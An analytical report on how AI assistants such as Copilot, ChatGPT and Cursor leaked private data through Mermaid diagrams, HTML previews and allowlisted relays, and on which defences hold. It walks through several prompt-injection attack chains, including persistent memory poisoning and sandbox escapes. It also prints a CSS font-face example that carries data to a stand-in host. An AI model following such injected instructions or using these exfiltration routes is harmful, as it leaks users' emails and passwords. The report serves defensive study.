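| CVE-2026-41159 | Add styles and fonts for the whole page through font and theme settings | 10.9.6 and 11.15.0 | `sandbox`, or protecting those settings |
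| CVE-2026-50159 | Style elements next to the drawing | 10.9.8 and 11.16.1 | `sandbox`, protecting the same settings, or giving the drawing its own container |

Other Mermaid advisories from August cover flaws unrelated to styling. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Mermaid package* lists one in XY charts that could freeze or crash the page, and OSV's *CVE-2026-71439* (2026) describes a similar problem in radar diagrams. NVD's *CVE-2026-71437* covers prototype pollution in architecture diagrams, a flaw that lets outside input change properties shared by many of a program's JavaScript objects.

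### Assistants with the affected versions

Applications usually include their own copy of Mermaid, so users can't fix a flaw in it until the application's developers release an update. LibreChat is one AI chat application known to have included an affected version. Chainguard found Mermaid 11.14.0 in the LibreChat package it supplies to customers and fixed the package on 18 May, a week after the advisories came out. Chainguard's *CGA-c8r4-7rw7-32cm* lists the same package under CVE-2026-41159.

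Those entries show that the package contained the faulty code, but not that an attacker could have stolen anything from a LibreChat user. Theft would also depend on LibreChat's CSP and on what its page kept in attributes. OSV links CVE-2026-41148 to 58 Chainguard advisories in all, which gives some idea of how widely other software relies on Mermaid. Companies that sell closed assistants rarely publish which version of a library they use, so outsiders can't easily check them.

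There is no public evidence that anyone used these flaws against an AI assistant. CISA recorded no known exploitation of either flaw, according to CIRCL's *CVE-2026-41148* and MITRE's *CVE-2026-41159*. CISA assessed CVE-2026-41159 on 29 May, the day its record appeared, so that assessment is weak evidence about later attacks.

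## HTML previews: the same leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot and ChatGPT

Microsoft removed links from Copilot's diagrams in September 2025. At about the same time, Copilot gained an HTML preview, which let users see web pages the model wrote inside the chat. ChatGPT gained a similar preview in February 2026. Researchers got private data out through both, so the previews are a good test of whether vendors that had already fixed image or diagram leaks were checking new renderers for the same problem.

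### Background images and fonts in Copilot

Johann Rehberger noticed Copilot's preview in September or October 2025. According to Embrace The Red, it didn't look exploitable at first. When he asked for a page with a heading and a picture from his own server, Copilot removed the image tag, so only the heading appeared. Copilot also showed the page's code by default, so nothing could load until the user switched to the preview.

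He then asked Copilot to write a page using every method it could think of to load something from another server. One of them worked. It was a background image in a style rule, which Mermaid's `themeCSS` setting also allows. With more help from Copilot he found that fonts worked too. For example, a page about the surprise party could put the venue in the address of a font:

```
@font-face { font-family: Party; src: url("https://example.com/bluebell-barn.woff2"); }
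h1 { font-family: Party; }
```

The browser needs the font to draw the heading, so it requests a file named after the venue from example.com. The file doesn't have to exist. If it doesn't, the browser uses another typeface and the page still looks normal.

Microsoft's developers had probably removed image tags because they knew that images could leak data, but they left at least two other ways of writing an outside address.

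### How the preview opened without a click

Rehberger got past the code view by adding a few words to the injected instructions, telling Copilot to show the preview once it had written the page. He called this naive, but it worked reliably. Copilot could switch to the preview itself, so the leak no longer needed a click from the user.

His demonstration in Word went like this:

1. The attacker shares a Word document containing hidden instructions. The victim opens it and types "hi there" to Copilot.
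2. Copilot follows the instructions and searches the victim's mailbox for an email about a code.
3. It writes a small web page, puts the text of the email into the address of a font, and opens the preview.
4. Word requests the font, and the attacker's server records the email.

Logue's victim had to ask for a summary and then click a login button, whereas here a greeting was enough.

Rehberger also made the attack outlast the conversation. He hid instructions in a biography of Albert Einstein, which made Copilot end its summary by asking whether the information was helpful. When the user answered yes or no, Copilot saved a memory with an instruction to put any password or code into the font address of an HTML preview. The user could close the biography and start a new chat days later, and Copilot would still leak the next password they pasted. Memory was on by default, and according to Microsoft's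 documentation, changes to it left no entries in the audit log, so a security team couldn't have found the planted memory there.

### Why Copilot's CSP depended on the host

Microsoft puts Copilot inside many sites, including Copilot's own chat site, SharePoint, and the online versions of Word and Excel. The browser takes the CSP from the site that serves the page, so Copilot had several CSPs, each with its own allowlist. An answer containing a background image could be harmless on the chat site and leak data in Excel, or the other way round.

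The lists for images were also long. In 2023 Microsoft had permitted images in Bing Chat from only four addresses. A policy for a whole office application has to cover everything the application loads, so it is likely to permit far more than a chat assistant needs. Rehberger found addresses on azureedge.net, a Microsoft domain where customers also run their own sites, and addresses for test versions of Microsoft's products. Some entries contained what appeared to be employees' user names. He concluded that Microsoft wasn't controlling the lists tightly. An attacker who gained control of any permitted address could have collected data there, much as Rehberger had used a permitted Google domain against Bard.

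He considered mapping what each site permitted, but didn't need to, because Copilot's policies were even looser for fonts than for images and let the preview load a font directly from his server. He demonstrated the theft in the desktop version of Word and in the online versions of Word and Excel.

Rehberger advises companies that sell assistants for use inside other sites to state clearly whether the assistant or the site is responsible for preventing leaks. Here Microsoft owned both the assistant and the site, and the protection still varied.

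### 140 days to a fix

Rehberger sent Microsoft his first report on 16 October 2025, and the main events after that were:

- **20 October:** he realised that the CSP varied between hosts.
- **12 November:** Microsoft confirmed that it could reproduce the leak.
- **19 November:** he sent the version that used Copilot's memory.
- **6 December:** Microsoft reported that it had fixed the memory attack.
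- **25 February 2026:** Microsoft was rolling out a fix for the preview.
- **5 March:** Microsoft marked the leak as resolved.

The fix took 140 days, compared with 42 for Logue's diagram and 68 for the Bing Chat image leak in 2023. Microsoft took 27 days to reproduce the leak, so it knew for the remaining 113 that the attack worked. Neither Microsoft nor Rehberger explains the delay. The number of hosts may be part of the reason, because correcting the CSP on one site would not have fixed the others.

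Rehberger suspected that Microsoft had dealt with the memory attack by training the model and blocking incoming malicious content. If so, a memory planted before the December fix could have kept leaking passwords until the March fix, unless the user found and deleted it.

Microsoft published the flaw as CVE-2026-24299 on 19 March. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) gives it a CVSS score of 5.3, based on high attack complexity, no required privileges and some user interaction. The same ratings would give Cursor's first Mermaid flaw the same score. Rehberger calls his attack zero-click, but the user interaction in Microsoft's rating may just be opening the malicious document. Microsoft classed the leak as command injection, a third category for much the same problem.

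Neither the record nor Rehberger describes the fix, though Rehberger gives its date. The fix did not end this type of leak in Copilot. In June 2026 the security company Varonis published SearchLeak, a one-click attack that stole emails, calendar data and files. Taler (2026), in *SearchLeak*, describes it as a chain of three flaws. One was a prompt injection, and The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* identifies the others as a race condition in the code that cleaned Copilot's HTML and a server-side request forgery in Bing.

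The HTML preview is weak evidence that Microsoft ignored the lesson of Logue's diagram, because it appeared within weeks of the diagram fix and Microsoft had probably designed it earlier. SearchLeak is stronger evidence, because it became public about nine months after the fix, which gave Microsoft time to check how Copilot handled HTML elsewhere.

### ChatGPT's preview and Lockdown Mode

OpenAI treated its preview as dangerous from the start. ChatGPT ran the page inside two nested, sandboxed iframes so that the page couldn't read the user's cookies or anything else ChatGPT had stored in the browser. If the page tried to load something from another server, ChatGPT asked the user for permission. OpenAI had been dealing with image leaks since 2023, so these precautions may not have been a response to the diagram attacks on other companies' products.

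For extra protection, users with sensitive data could use an optional setting called Lockdown Mode. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it for organisations on 13 February, the same month the preview appeared. OpenAI extended it to personal accounts in June.

Lockdown Mode limits the requests that could carry data out after a prompt injection succeeds. It isn't designed to stop the injections themselves. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, with the mode on, ChatGPT reads stored copies of web pages instead of live ones, may not show images in ordinary answers, and cannot download files for analysis. Deep research and agent mode, which let ChatGPT carry out longer tasks on the web, are off. These restrictions don't depend on the model recognising an attack. Willison (2026), whose lethal trifecta includes a way to send data out, wrote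 that the setting "looks really good to me".

OpenAI said in its announcement that it had turned some features off completely because it could not offer "strong deterministic guarantees of data safety". The HTML preview stayed on. According to OpenAI's list of restrictions, users in Lockdown Mode cannot approve network access in Canvas, a panel for editing text and code. The list doesn't mention previews of code blocks, but *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* (Willison, 2026) describes them as apparently the latest version of Canvas, so OpenAI may have meant the restriction to apply to both.

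### A window outside the sandbox

Researchers at the security company Check Point found that a previewed page could open a new window outside the sandbox. ChatGPT's code intercepted the usual way of opening a window and showed the user a prompt first. But the browser enforces the sandbox's permissions separately, and those permissions still let the page open new windows that were free of the sandbox's restrictions. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) quotes Check Point as saying that a page could bypass ChatGPT's code and open a window that Lockdown Mode did not restrict. The request to load the new window's page could carry stolen data.

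Browsers normally block new windows until the user clicks something. *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations* (Loupia, 2026) also reports that ChatGPT Classic, an older desktop application built on Electron, did not block them. In that application, Check Point used a malicious custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that someone sets up with their own instructions and shares, to send the chat history to an outside server while the user was talking to it. As with Dify's public chatbots, the attacker was the chatbot's maker, so they didn't need a prompt injection. A malicious prompt or a shared chat could also deliver the page.

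An attacker could also use the window to deceive people. Duggan (2026), in *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup*, explains that the window kept ChatGPT's icon while the attacker chose its title and contents, so the attacker could disguise it as a ChatGPT update and offer malware. In another demonstration, Check Point signed the user out of the desktop application and showed an attacker-controlled login page to steal the user's password.

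On 18 September 2026 OpenAI told Check Point that it had removed both permissions from the outer iframe. This was better than improving the code that intercepted windows, because the browser now blocks new windows whatever method the page uses to open them. Check Point confirmed that its method no longer worked and published its findings on 5 November. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that OpenAI made the change on its servers, so users had nothing to install. Check Point reported no real attacks using the flaw.

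OpenAI warns on its help page that Lockdown Mode cannot guarantee that data won't be stolen, and lists "unforeseen combinations of capabilities" as one remaining risk. In October, a different research team found such a combination in the same preview.

### A graph and a preview

*Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) describes how the team at the security company Parameter combined an HTML preview with an interactive graph. ChatGPT loaded a mathematics library into its main page to draw the graph. The library accepted messages without checking who had sent them, so the preview could send it HTML from inside the sandbox, and the library added that HTML to the main page. ChatGPT's CSP blocked most outside scripts but allowed those from YouTube, and the team found a way to make a YouTube address return their own code.

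The attacker put the graph and the preview in one conversation and shared the link. If a logged-in user opened the link, the attacker's script ran with access to that user's account. The team's script listed the victim's conversations, opened a private one and sent its contents to another server. Like the scripts in Dify, it didn't need the model to supply the data.

OpenAI fixed the flaw on 26 October, just over five weeks after it closed Check Point's route. This attack got out of the sandbox through a message, so removing the permission to open windows could not have prevented it. OpenAI paid a $5,000 bounty, which Willison thought "a bit cheap" for such a serious flaw.

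### What the previews share with Mermaid

ChatGPT uses the same feature to preview web pages and diagrams. OpenAI's *Working with writing blocks and code blocks in ChatGPT* lists HTML pages, Mermaid diagrams, SVG images and charts among the code blocks that users can preview. The model writes a block of code, which does nothing until the application renders it as live content.

Showing the code first is not a useful safeguard when an attacker can open the preview without the user. In Copilot, a sentence in the injected instructions opened it. In ChatGPT, victims of the October attack at first had to click a "Preview" button, but Goyal's team then marked the block so that ChatGPT opened the preview automatically. Chat assistants often draw Mermaid diagrams without showing the code first, and Cursor drew Rehberger's as soon as the model had written it.

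HTML is much harder to restrict than Mermaid. A web page can load images, fonts, style sheets, videos and other pages, and in ChatGPT's preview it can also run scripts. Removing all of these would make many pages look wrong or stop working.

Isolating the page, as OpenAI did, lets the page keep most of its features and also made the attacker's work harder. Check Point had to find a way out of two nested sandboxes, while Rehberger found his first gap in Copilot's filter by asking Copilot to look for one. But code unrelated to the preview can break the isolation, as happened when ChatGPT loaded a library for drawing graphs.

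## Why diagram renderers were missed after the image fixes

When Johann Rehberger reported the diagram leak in Cursor in June 2025, vendors had been fixing image leaks in AI assistants for two years. None of them has explained publicly why diagrams still leaked. The cases suggest five possible reasons:

1. The image fixes dealt with Markdown images and left other outgoing requests alone.
2. A diagram reaches the page as a block of code, and a separate library turns it into a picture after the application has cleaned the text.
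3. Programmers built diagram libraries for people writing their own documents, and application developers then loosened the settings to make diagrams look better.
4. Low severity scores and narrow bounty programmes gave researchers little reason to look.
5. Companies released new display features faster than they reviewed them.

The evidence for these explanations is uneven. Copilot's HTML preview shows directly that a fix could cover image tags and little else. GitHub's documentation shows how a diagram is passed along as code, but nobody has confirmed that this caused the leaks in Cursor or Copilot. Loosened settings are a documented cause only in Dify. The explanations about rewards and speed are mostly inference.

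### Fixes that covered one kind of image

Copilot's preview removed image tags but still loaded background images and fonts. A similar gap had already appeared in Copilot's ordinary answers. In June 2025 researchers published EchoLeak, an attack in which a malicious email made Copilot leak private data through an image. Willison describes two weaknesses that let the image through:

- Markdown has another way of writing an image, which gives the picture a short name and puts its address on a separate line. Copilot's defences missed it.
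- Copilot's CSP blocked images from unknown sites, but the allowlist included a Microsoft Teams domain that would forward a request to any server.

The missed notation fits the explanation well. The Teams domain doesn't, because the data still got out even though a content security policy (CSP) applies to requests however the model writes the address. Blocking requests helps only if the list of permitted addresses is short.

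Researchers were still finding image leaks in Copilot in 2026. ReLeak, a set of zero-click attacks that Cato AI Labs published that December, began with an email that the victim never had to open. *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (AIAIAI.FYI, 2026) reports that data could get out through the address of an image, a link to a saved file, or a piece of code. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes the researchers as saying that "too little progress has been made" in the year since they exposed a similar flaw. Microsoft had fixed particular image leaks before Copilot's diagrams leaked, but images could still be used to send data out.

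Adam Logue's login button used a link, so even a perfect fix for images would not have stopped it. But Microsoft had also been warned about links, because the attack that Embrace The Red reported to it in 2024 ended with Copilot displaying a link that contained stolen data. The Cursor leak is weaker evidence that diagram renderers were missed after an image fix, because Rehberger's account doesn't say whether the editor had ever blocked Markdown images.

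Programmers also overlook neighbouring features in non-AI software. aphantom (2025) reported in *CVE-2025-12029 Variant* that GitLab had fixed a flaw in its sandbox for Swagger, a tool that displays API documentation, but had left the same flaw in its sandbox for Mermaid. According to the report, GitLab only needed to copy a few lines of code from the Swagger sandbox to the Mermaid one.

### A diagram is only text when the application cleans it

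According to GitHub's *Include diagrams in your Markdown files with Mermaid* (2022), a filter replaces each code block labelled `mermaid` with an iframe when GitHub converts a Markdown file to HTML. Mermaid then draws the diagram inside the iframe, in the reader's browser.

A chat assistant that works in a similar order, but without the iframe, could leak the name of the party venue like this:

1. The model writes a code block labelled `mermaid`. One node has an image whose address contains `bluebell-barn`.
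2. The application converts the answer into HTML. Markdown displays code exactly as written, so the image's address is still only text.
3. The application cleans the HTML. It finds no image, so it removes nothing.
4. Mermaid reads the text and builds a drawing that does contain an image.
5. The browser requests the image from example.com.

At the end of step 4, Mermaid runs its own cleaning pass, which removes scripts but keeps ordinary images. The venue can therefore still reach the attacker even when both checks work as intended.

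Direct evidence shows that DeepChat missed diagrams at this point and AnythingLLM missed chart captions. We can only infer that Cursor and Microsoft 365 Copilot missed diagrams in the same way, because neither Cursor nor Microsoft has described the order in which its product cleaned and drew an answer.

Separate libraries can also let attackers bypass a good defence elsewhere on the page. According to The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026), the sandbox around the HTML preview held during the October 2026 attack on ChatGPT. The attackers got in through the MathLive library, which ChatGPT had loaded into its main page to draw a graph.

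The order of cleaning can't be the whole explanation, though. Copilot's HTML preview displayed ordinary HTML, which Microsoft did clean, and it leaked anyway.

### Settings for trusted authors

Dify is the only case where the reason for a weaker setting is on record. It chose `loose` for its colour themes. Open WebUI and 5ire also used `loose`, but the public records on their flaws don't include a reason.

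Isolation can make diagrams look worse and rendering less reliable. In 2026 a user reported to GitLab that every Mermaid diagram on its website had been replaced by a picture of a bomb with the words "Syntax error in text". The diagrams were valid, but a CSP was preventing GitLab's isolated frame from loading parts of its own code. A fault like this may tempt a developer to remove the isolation.

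Mermaid's developers had thought about hostile diagrams, so the claim that they expected only trusted authors is less convincing. By 2021 their code had a list of settings that a diagram could not change, and they wrote in a comment that the list was there to stop "malicious graph directives from overriding a site's default security". They also made `strict` the default. But their protections were aimed at scripts and HTML, and the image nodes they added later load remote pictures even under `strict`.

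In a documentation tool, an outside image in a flowchart is a small privacy problem because it can reveal a reader's IP address. Such images became a way to steal emails and passwords only when language models with access to that data began writing the diagrams.

### Kroki and PlantUML

Snyk found related flaws in two other diagram tools, which suggests that the weakness is general.

Kroki, a service that draws diagrams on a server, has a safe mode that should stop a diagram from loading files or web addresses. A Vega chart can list its data sources or give a single one, but Kroki checked only the lists. A chart with a single source could make Kroki open a file on its own server and show the contents in the picture. GitLab can be set up to use Kroki, and Snyk showed that the attack worked from a README file in a GitLab project. Kroki fixed the flaw, CVE-2025-14896, in version 0.29.1.

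Vega's developers had made this easier by adding local files to the pattern for permitted addresses that they copied from DOMPurify. Someone charting data on their own computer needs access to local files, but a server drawing charts for strangers should not allow it.

PlantUML accepts diagrams in DOT, a language for describing nodes and the lines between them. It searched these diagrams for JavaScript links and changed their prefix so that they wouldn't run. An attacker could evade the search by writing one letter of the prefix as a numeric code, much as with DeepChat. PlantUML's developers fixed the flaw, CVE-2026-0858, in version 1.2026.0 by no longer exporting DOT diagrams as SVG, so they didn't have to anticipate every spelling of the prefix.

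Neither flaw needs a language model, and the one in Kroki reads private data without sending it to another server. Both tools have the same basic problem as Mermaid. A description of a picture can include an address, and the programmers who checked it missed one way of writing the address. Snyk was looking for flaws of this kind, so its results can't show how common they are.

### Scores and bounties

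Low severity scores can't explain why Cursor's developers missed the leak, because GitHub published its score of 4.4 a month after Rehberger reported the flaw. At most, the score discouraged people from checking other products afterwards.

Bounty rules are a more plausible explanation because they were in place before anyone looked. Microsoft had no bounty programme covering Microsoft 365 Copilot. Logue and Rehberger investigated it anyway, but published cases come only from people who went ahead, so they don't show how many researchers read the rules and chose another target.

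GitLab is a rough comparison. At least two of its Mermaid flaws, including the one aphantom found, were reported through HackerOne, which runs bug bounty programmes. GitLab says it received so many reports of XSS in Mermaid that the programmer who isolated the diagrams looked forward to no longer getting "Found a new mermaid XSS vulnerability" emails. Rewards may have helped GitLab learn about the problem early. But GitLab also publishes its code and lets anybody upload a diagram, which makes it much easier to study than Copilot.

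The severity ratings of Mermaid's early flaws also fit this explanation, but only loosely. Mermaid's *Security* lists an XSS flaw from December 2021 as high severity and a styling flaw from June 2022 as moderate. The styling flaw could leak data through background images, so a developer who read only the high-severity advisories would have missed the warning most relevant to the later attacks.

### New features and late reviews

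Cursor began drawing Mermaid diagrams in its chat panel with version 1.0, released in June 2025 and covered in AlternativeTo's *Cursor 1.0 adds BugBot code reviews, project 'Memories', and Background Agent*. In *Render mermaid markdown in chat*, a thread on Cursor's forum, users had complained about having to copy diagrams into another file to see them, and one pointed out that a rival tool, Cline, already displayed them. Rehberger reported the leak on June 30, 2025.

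Cursor's *1.0* announced Memories and one-click connection to outside tools through MCP alongside diagram rendering. Rehberger stole Memories in one of his demonstrations. The release therefore gave attackers more data to steal, more places to plant an injection and a new way to send data out. Reviewers who looked at each feature separately could easily have missed how they worked together.

The timing was similar in other products. Microsoft (2025) announced on 11 September that Visual Studio users could ask Copilot for a Mermaid diagram and preview it in the editor. It released the Visual Studio update that it linked to Cursor's Mermaid flaw 33 days later, on 14 October. Rehberger reported the leak in Copilot's HTML preview within weeks of first seeing the feature.

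These dates show that outsiders found problems soon after new features appeared, but not whether the companies had reviewed the features first. Rehberger found the Cursor leak by asking for a diagram with an image in it, a test that would take a reviewer a minute. That suggests nobody at Cursor tried it, though someone may have done so and thought an external image was harmless.

Chi, whose company Archestra sells protection against such leaks, thinks the cause is how product teams plan their work. In *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags*, Chi calls rendering Markdown "a one-line product decision", and says routing every image through a restricted proxy is a small project that nobody finishes in the first week. This is plausible and would explain why the same flaw keeps appearing in new products, but Chi gives no evidence from inside any of the companies.

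Haste is a less convincing explanation for the flaws in ChatGPT's preview. OpenAI isolated the preview from the start, clearly with leaks in mind, but researchers still found two ways to get data out.

### Who already knew that Mermaid was risky

Security researchers and some large websites had known for years that Mermaid diagrams could be dangerous. In May 2021 a researcher called saleemrashid reported that a diagram on GitLab could take over the account of anyone who viewed it, without a click. GitLab used `strict` and had also turned off HTML in labels, but a diagram could set that option to the word "false" in quotation marks. One part of Mermaid treated this as off and skipped the cleaning, while another treated any text there as "on" and displayed the label as HTML.

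saleemrashid (2021), in *Stored XSS in Mermaid when viewing Markdown files*, also described trying to steal data through Mermaid's `themeCSS` setting. The attempt recovered only a few characters, because GitLab's CSP blocked style sheets from outside servers. This was four years before the Cursor leak, and it already used a diagram to send private data out. A year later GitHub Security Lab warned of the same danger from background images, in the flaw that became CVE-2022-31108.

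GitLab lists another advisory, from 2024, about a vulnerable copy of DOMPurify, the tool Mermaid included in its package to clean diagrams. OSV's *CVE-2025-54880* (2025) describes an XSS flaw in the icons of architecture diagrams. The flaw affected Mermaid's default configuration and became public on 19 August 2025, less than three weeks after the record of Cursor's leak.

GitHub isolated Mermaid in an iframe on a separate service from the day it introduced the feature in February 2022. Two of the three reasons in its announcement concern speed. The other is that content from users is "locked away" where it can do less harm to the surrounding page.

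GitLab isolated Mermaid only after repeated trouble. Its *Minimize security impact from mermaid XSS* calls the library "a security problem" and lists three options: cleaning the finished SVG, using a sandboxed iframe, or replacing Mermaid with another product. GitLab chose the iframe, as saleemrashid had suggested. GitLab's *FY22Q4 OKR*, a plan for the quarter that ended in January 2022, records that GitLab released the sandbox on its own site and to customers who run GitLab themselves. Gitea, another code-hosting application, also moved its diagrams into an iframe "for improved security", according to its *Various Mermaid improvements*.

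All of this was publicly available to anyone adding Mermaid to a chat assistant in 2025. Microsoft had even less excuse for missing it, because it has owned GitHub since 2018. Web security researchers had been using Mermaid diagrams to send data out since 2021, so Rehberger's description of images in the diagrams as "a new variant" of the image leak was true only for AI assistants.

Copying GitHub or GitLab might not have prevented the later leaks, however. Their iframes protect the page from the diagram by stopping scripts inside the frame from reading the user's account details outside it. In the attacks on Cursor and Copilot, the diagram didn't have to read anything, because the model had already written the private data into it. Loading an image or opening a link from the frame is then enough to leak the data. An automated test quoted in GitLab's *Failure* shows that GitLab's iframe permits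 links that open in new windows. That is reasonable when a person wrote the diagram, but if an assistant wrote it after reading an attacker's email, the link may contain the user's data.

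## How the patches compare and which defences hold

Most of the patches blocked one way of contacting an outside server and left others open. The table lists the patches roughly in date order, with the time from the researcher's report to the fix.

| Patch | What it removed | Time to fix | What could still send data |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cursor 1.3, July 2025 | Some remote images in diagrams; no details published | 29 days | Remote images, by other routes |
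| Copilot's diagrams, September 2025 | Links | 42 days | Background images and fonts, in the new HTML preview |
| Cursor 1.7, by October 2025 | The other known routes for remote images | Not public | Not documented |
| Dify 1.11.2, flaw published March 2026 | Clicking, and HTML in labels | Not public | Image nodes and background images, if no CSP blocked them |
| Copilot's HTML preview, March 2026 | Not published | 140 days | Images, through Bing |
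| Mermaid 11.15.0, May 2026 | Styles and HTML that escaped from a diagram | Not public | Image nodes, and probably background images |
| Copilot's SearchLeak flaw, June 2026 | Not published | Not public | Images, again through Bing |
| ChatGPT's preview, September 2026 | Permission to open new windows | Not public | A script in the main page, until 26 October |
| Copilot's three ReLeak flaws, September to November 2026 | Not published | Between 28 and 109 days | Not known |

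The time a company took to fix the problem did not necessarily show how thorough the fix was. Cursor resolved the first report in a week, according to Embrace The Red, and then needed a second fix. Microsoft spent far longer on the HTML preview, and researchers were still getting data out of Copilot through images that summer.

The time to fix is also a poor measure of when users became safe. Microsoft and OpenAI could change their own servers, which protected everyone at once. Cursor's users waited 22 days for a release after the developers resolved the flaw, and the fixes in Dify and Mermaid protect only people who install them.

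Outsiders can judge only some of these patches, because vendors rarely explain them. Microsoft's removal of links from Copilot's diagrams is an exception.

### Five defences against three kinds of request

The table shows how well five general defences stop the three kinds of request a diagram can cause: fetching an image when the diagram is displayed, loading a background image or font named in a style rule, and opening a link the user clicks.

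| Defence | Images on display | Style and font loads | Clicked links |
|---|---|---|---|
| Removing features | Stops them if developers find every notation | Stops them if developers find every notation | Stops them |
| `strict` setting | Stops only HTML images | Does not stop them | Stops them, according to the documentation |
| Sandboxed iframe without network access | Stops them | Stops them | Stops them, with the right permissions |
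| Fixed picture | Stops them in the browser | Stops them in the browser | Stops them |
| CSP on the whole page | Stops them, except from permitted sites | Stops them, except from permitted sites | Does not stop them |

Removing a feature works well when developers can remove all of it. Microsoft did this with links, and users lost little. Images are harder to remove because Mermaid can include them in several ways, and a new version can add another, as version 11.3.0 did with image nodes. The only complete version of this defence is to show the diagram's description as text instead of drawing it, which is a serious loss for users who wanted a picture.

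According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy*, the program that cleans Gemini's Markdown identifies the addresses of outside images and doesn't display the images, so users no longer see pictures from other websites in Gemini's answers. That program works on Markdown, so diagrams would need a separate check.

The `strict` setting is already the default and removes only clickable nodes and HTML formatting in labels, so users lose very little. It was a good choice for Dify, whose problem was scripts in links, but it is a poor defence against exfiltration because image nodes and background images still load without a click.

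A sandbox can stop the page in an iframe from running scripts, opening windows or replacing the surrounding page, but the browser still loads the page's images and fonts, including those from outside addresses. To block those requests, the developer gives the framed page its own CSP that permits no outside addresses. This policy can be much stricter than one for the whole application, because a diagram needs only shapes, text and styles, all of which can already be in the frame.

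The developer also has to restrict links in the frame by withholding its permissions to open windows and to replace the surrounding page. A clicked link could still open inside the frame and send the same request, so the surrounding page also needs a CSP that limits which pages its frames may load. Mermaid must draw inside the frame too. If it draws in the main page and the application moves the result into the frame, the browser may already have requested the image.

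Together, these measures block all three kinds of request, but users lose outside pictures and working links. Diagrams may also clash with the application's colours, which is why Dify abandoned the sandbox. A mistake in the policy can stop diagrams from appearing at all, as happened to the GitLab user who saw bomb icons.

The application can also draw the diagram somewhere else and send the chat window a finished picture. A PNG file is a grid of coloured dots, so it can't contain a working link or make the browser load anything else. If the party plan included a map from example.com, the user would see a box with a blank space in it. An SVG stays sharp when the user zooms in, and it can be almost as safe as a PNG if the application displays it through an ordinary image tag, because browsers then don't run the drawing's scripts, load outside files for it or let the user click its links.

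But the program that draws the picture also needs to be offline. Otherwise it will request the map itself, and the attacker will learn the venue from the server's request instead of the browser's. Snyk's attack on Kroki showed that a drawing server can be tricked into opening files, and one of the three ReLeak attacks on Copilot showed that a server can leak data after the user has finished. In that attack, Copilot saved a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with confidential data. Microsoft's servers then processed the file in the background and sent the data out. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, reports that this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the employee never opened the file.

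Readers can't select or search the words in a fixed picture such as a PNG, and screen readers, which read text aloud to blind users, can't read them. An application can solve both problems by offering the diagram's text beside the picture. Drawing the diagram on a server also takes time and reveals its contents to that server, which matters if another company runs it.

A CSP on the whole page covers every renderer, including any that developers add later. It has to restrict fonts and styles as well as images, as Johann Rehberger's font leak in Copilot showed. But it also blocks pictures from unlisted sites throughout the application. Vendors can add sites to the list, but each addition gives attackers another possible route.

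A CSP doesn't restrict ordinary links. It also protects only pages that the vendor controls, so it can't stop a messaging service from fetching link previews. PromptArmor found that an assistant called OpenClaw was exposed by default to leaks through these previews when it replied through Telegram.

The best protection for a chat assistant that draws diagrams is therefore to show each diagram in a frame without network access or as a fixed picture, with a CSP on the whole page for everything else. Neither the frame nor the picture depends on the developers knowing every way a diagram can include an address.

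### When a permitted site passes the request on

An allowlist can fail even when the browser enforces it perfectly. Suppose the chat window may load images only from a search engine, and the search engine lets people look up a picture by giving its web address. An attacker could still learn the party venue:

1. The model writes an image whose address belongs to the search engine. Inside that address is a second one, on example.com, containing the venue's name.
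2. The browser checks the first address, finds the search engine on its list and sends the request.
3. The search engine's server fetches the picture at the second address, because it needs the picture to look for similar ones.
4. The server at example.com records the request, including the name of the venue.

A CSP restricts requests from the user's browser, not from the search engine's server. A simple redirect from a permitted site wouldn't get around the CSP, because browsers also check the redirect's destination against it. But an application that checks addresses itself may check only the first one, which OpenAI gives as one reason that lists of trusted sites aren't enough.

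SearchLeak, Varonis's attack of June 2026, used Bing in this way. Copilot's CSP allowed images from Bing, and Bing's image search fetched any picture it was asked to analyse. Unlike in Adam Logue's attack, the victim clicked at the start, on a link to Microsoft's own site. The link contained a search query that Copilot treated as instructions. Copilot searched the victim's email and wrote the title of a message into an image address. Email titles sometimes contain login codes.

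Copilot's other defence turned any HTML in an answer into harmless code, but only after the model had finished writing. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so by then it had already requested the image. Taler recommends cleaning the output as the application displays it. Anyone who tested Copilot by reading the finished answer would have seen only the harmless code. A more reliable test records outgoing requests. *Silent Egress (2026)* did this by asking a small model to summarise web pages and logging the requests that reached an attacker's server.

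Microsoft assigned the flaw CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June 2026. It rated the flaw critical, although the CVSS score was only 6.5, partly because the attack requires a click. According to The Next Web, Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers and knew of no malicious use. The Next Web also describes an earlier attack by Taler, called Reprompt, which put instructions in a link to the consumer version of Copilot. Microsoft received a report of it in August 2025 and patched the flaw in January 2026, but the technique still worked in the business version.

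Cato AI Labs soon used Bing to get data out of Copilot again, in one of the three attacks that *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) describes. When the victim asked Copilot an ordinary question about work, Copilot found the attacker's unopened email and followed the instructions in it. It then put confidential data into an image address. When the browser loaded the image, Bing passed the data to the attacker's server.

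Cato reported the three flaws between 29 July and 20 August 2026, after Varonis had published SearchLeak. Faisal gives the dates of the fixes:

- **17 September:** the code interpreter, where Copilot runs programs (CVE-2026-78501).
- **11 November:** the files that Copilot created (CVE-2026-124132).
- **15 November:** the images that went through Bing (CVE-2026-124115).

The last fix came 164 days after Microsoft assigned SearchLeak its identifier. Microsoft may have fixed SearchLeak by changing how Copilot handled links or cleaned its answers, while leaving Bing on the list of permitted sites. Or it may have closed one way of making Bing fetch an address and missed another. Either would explain why a second team could use Bing after the first fix, but it is unclear from the public accounts which happened.

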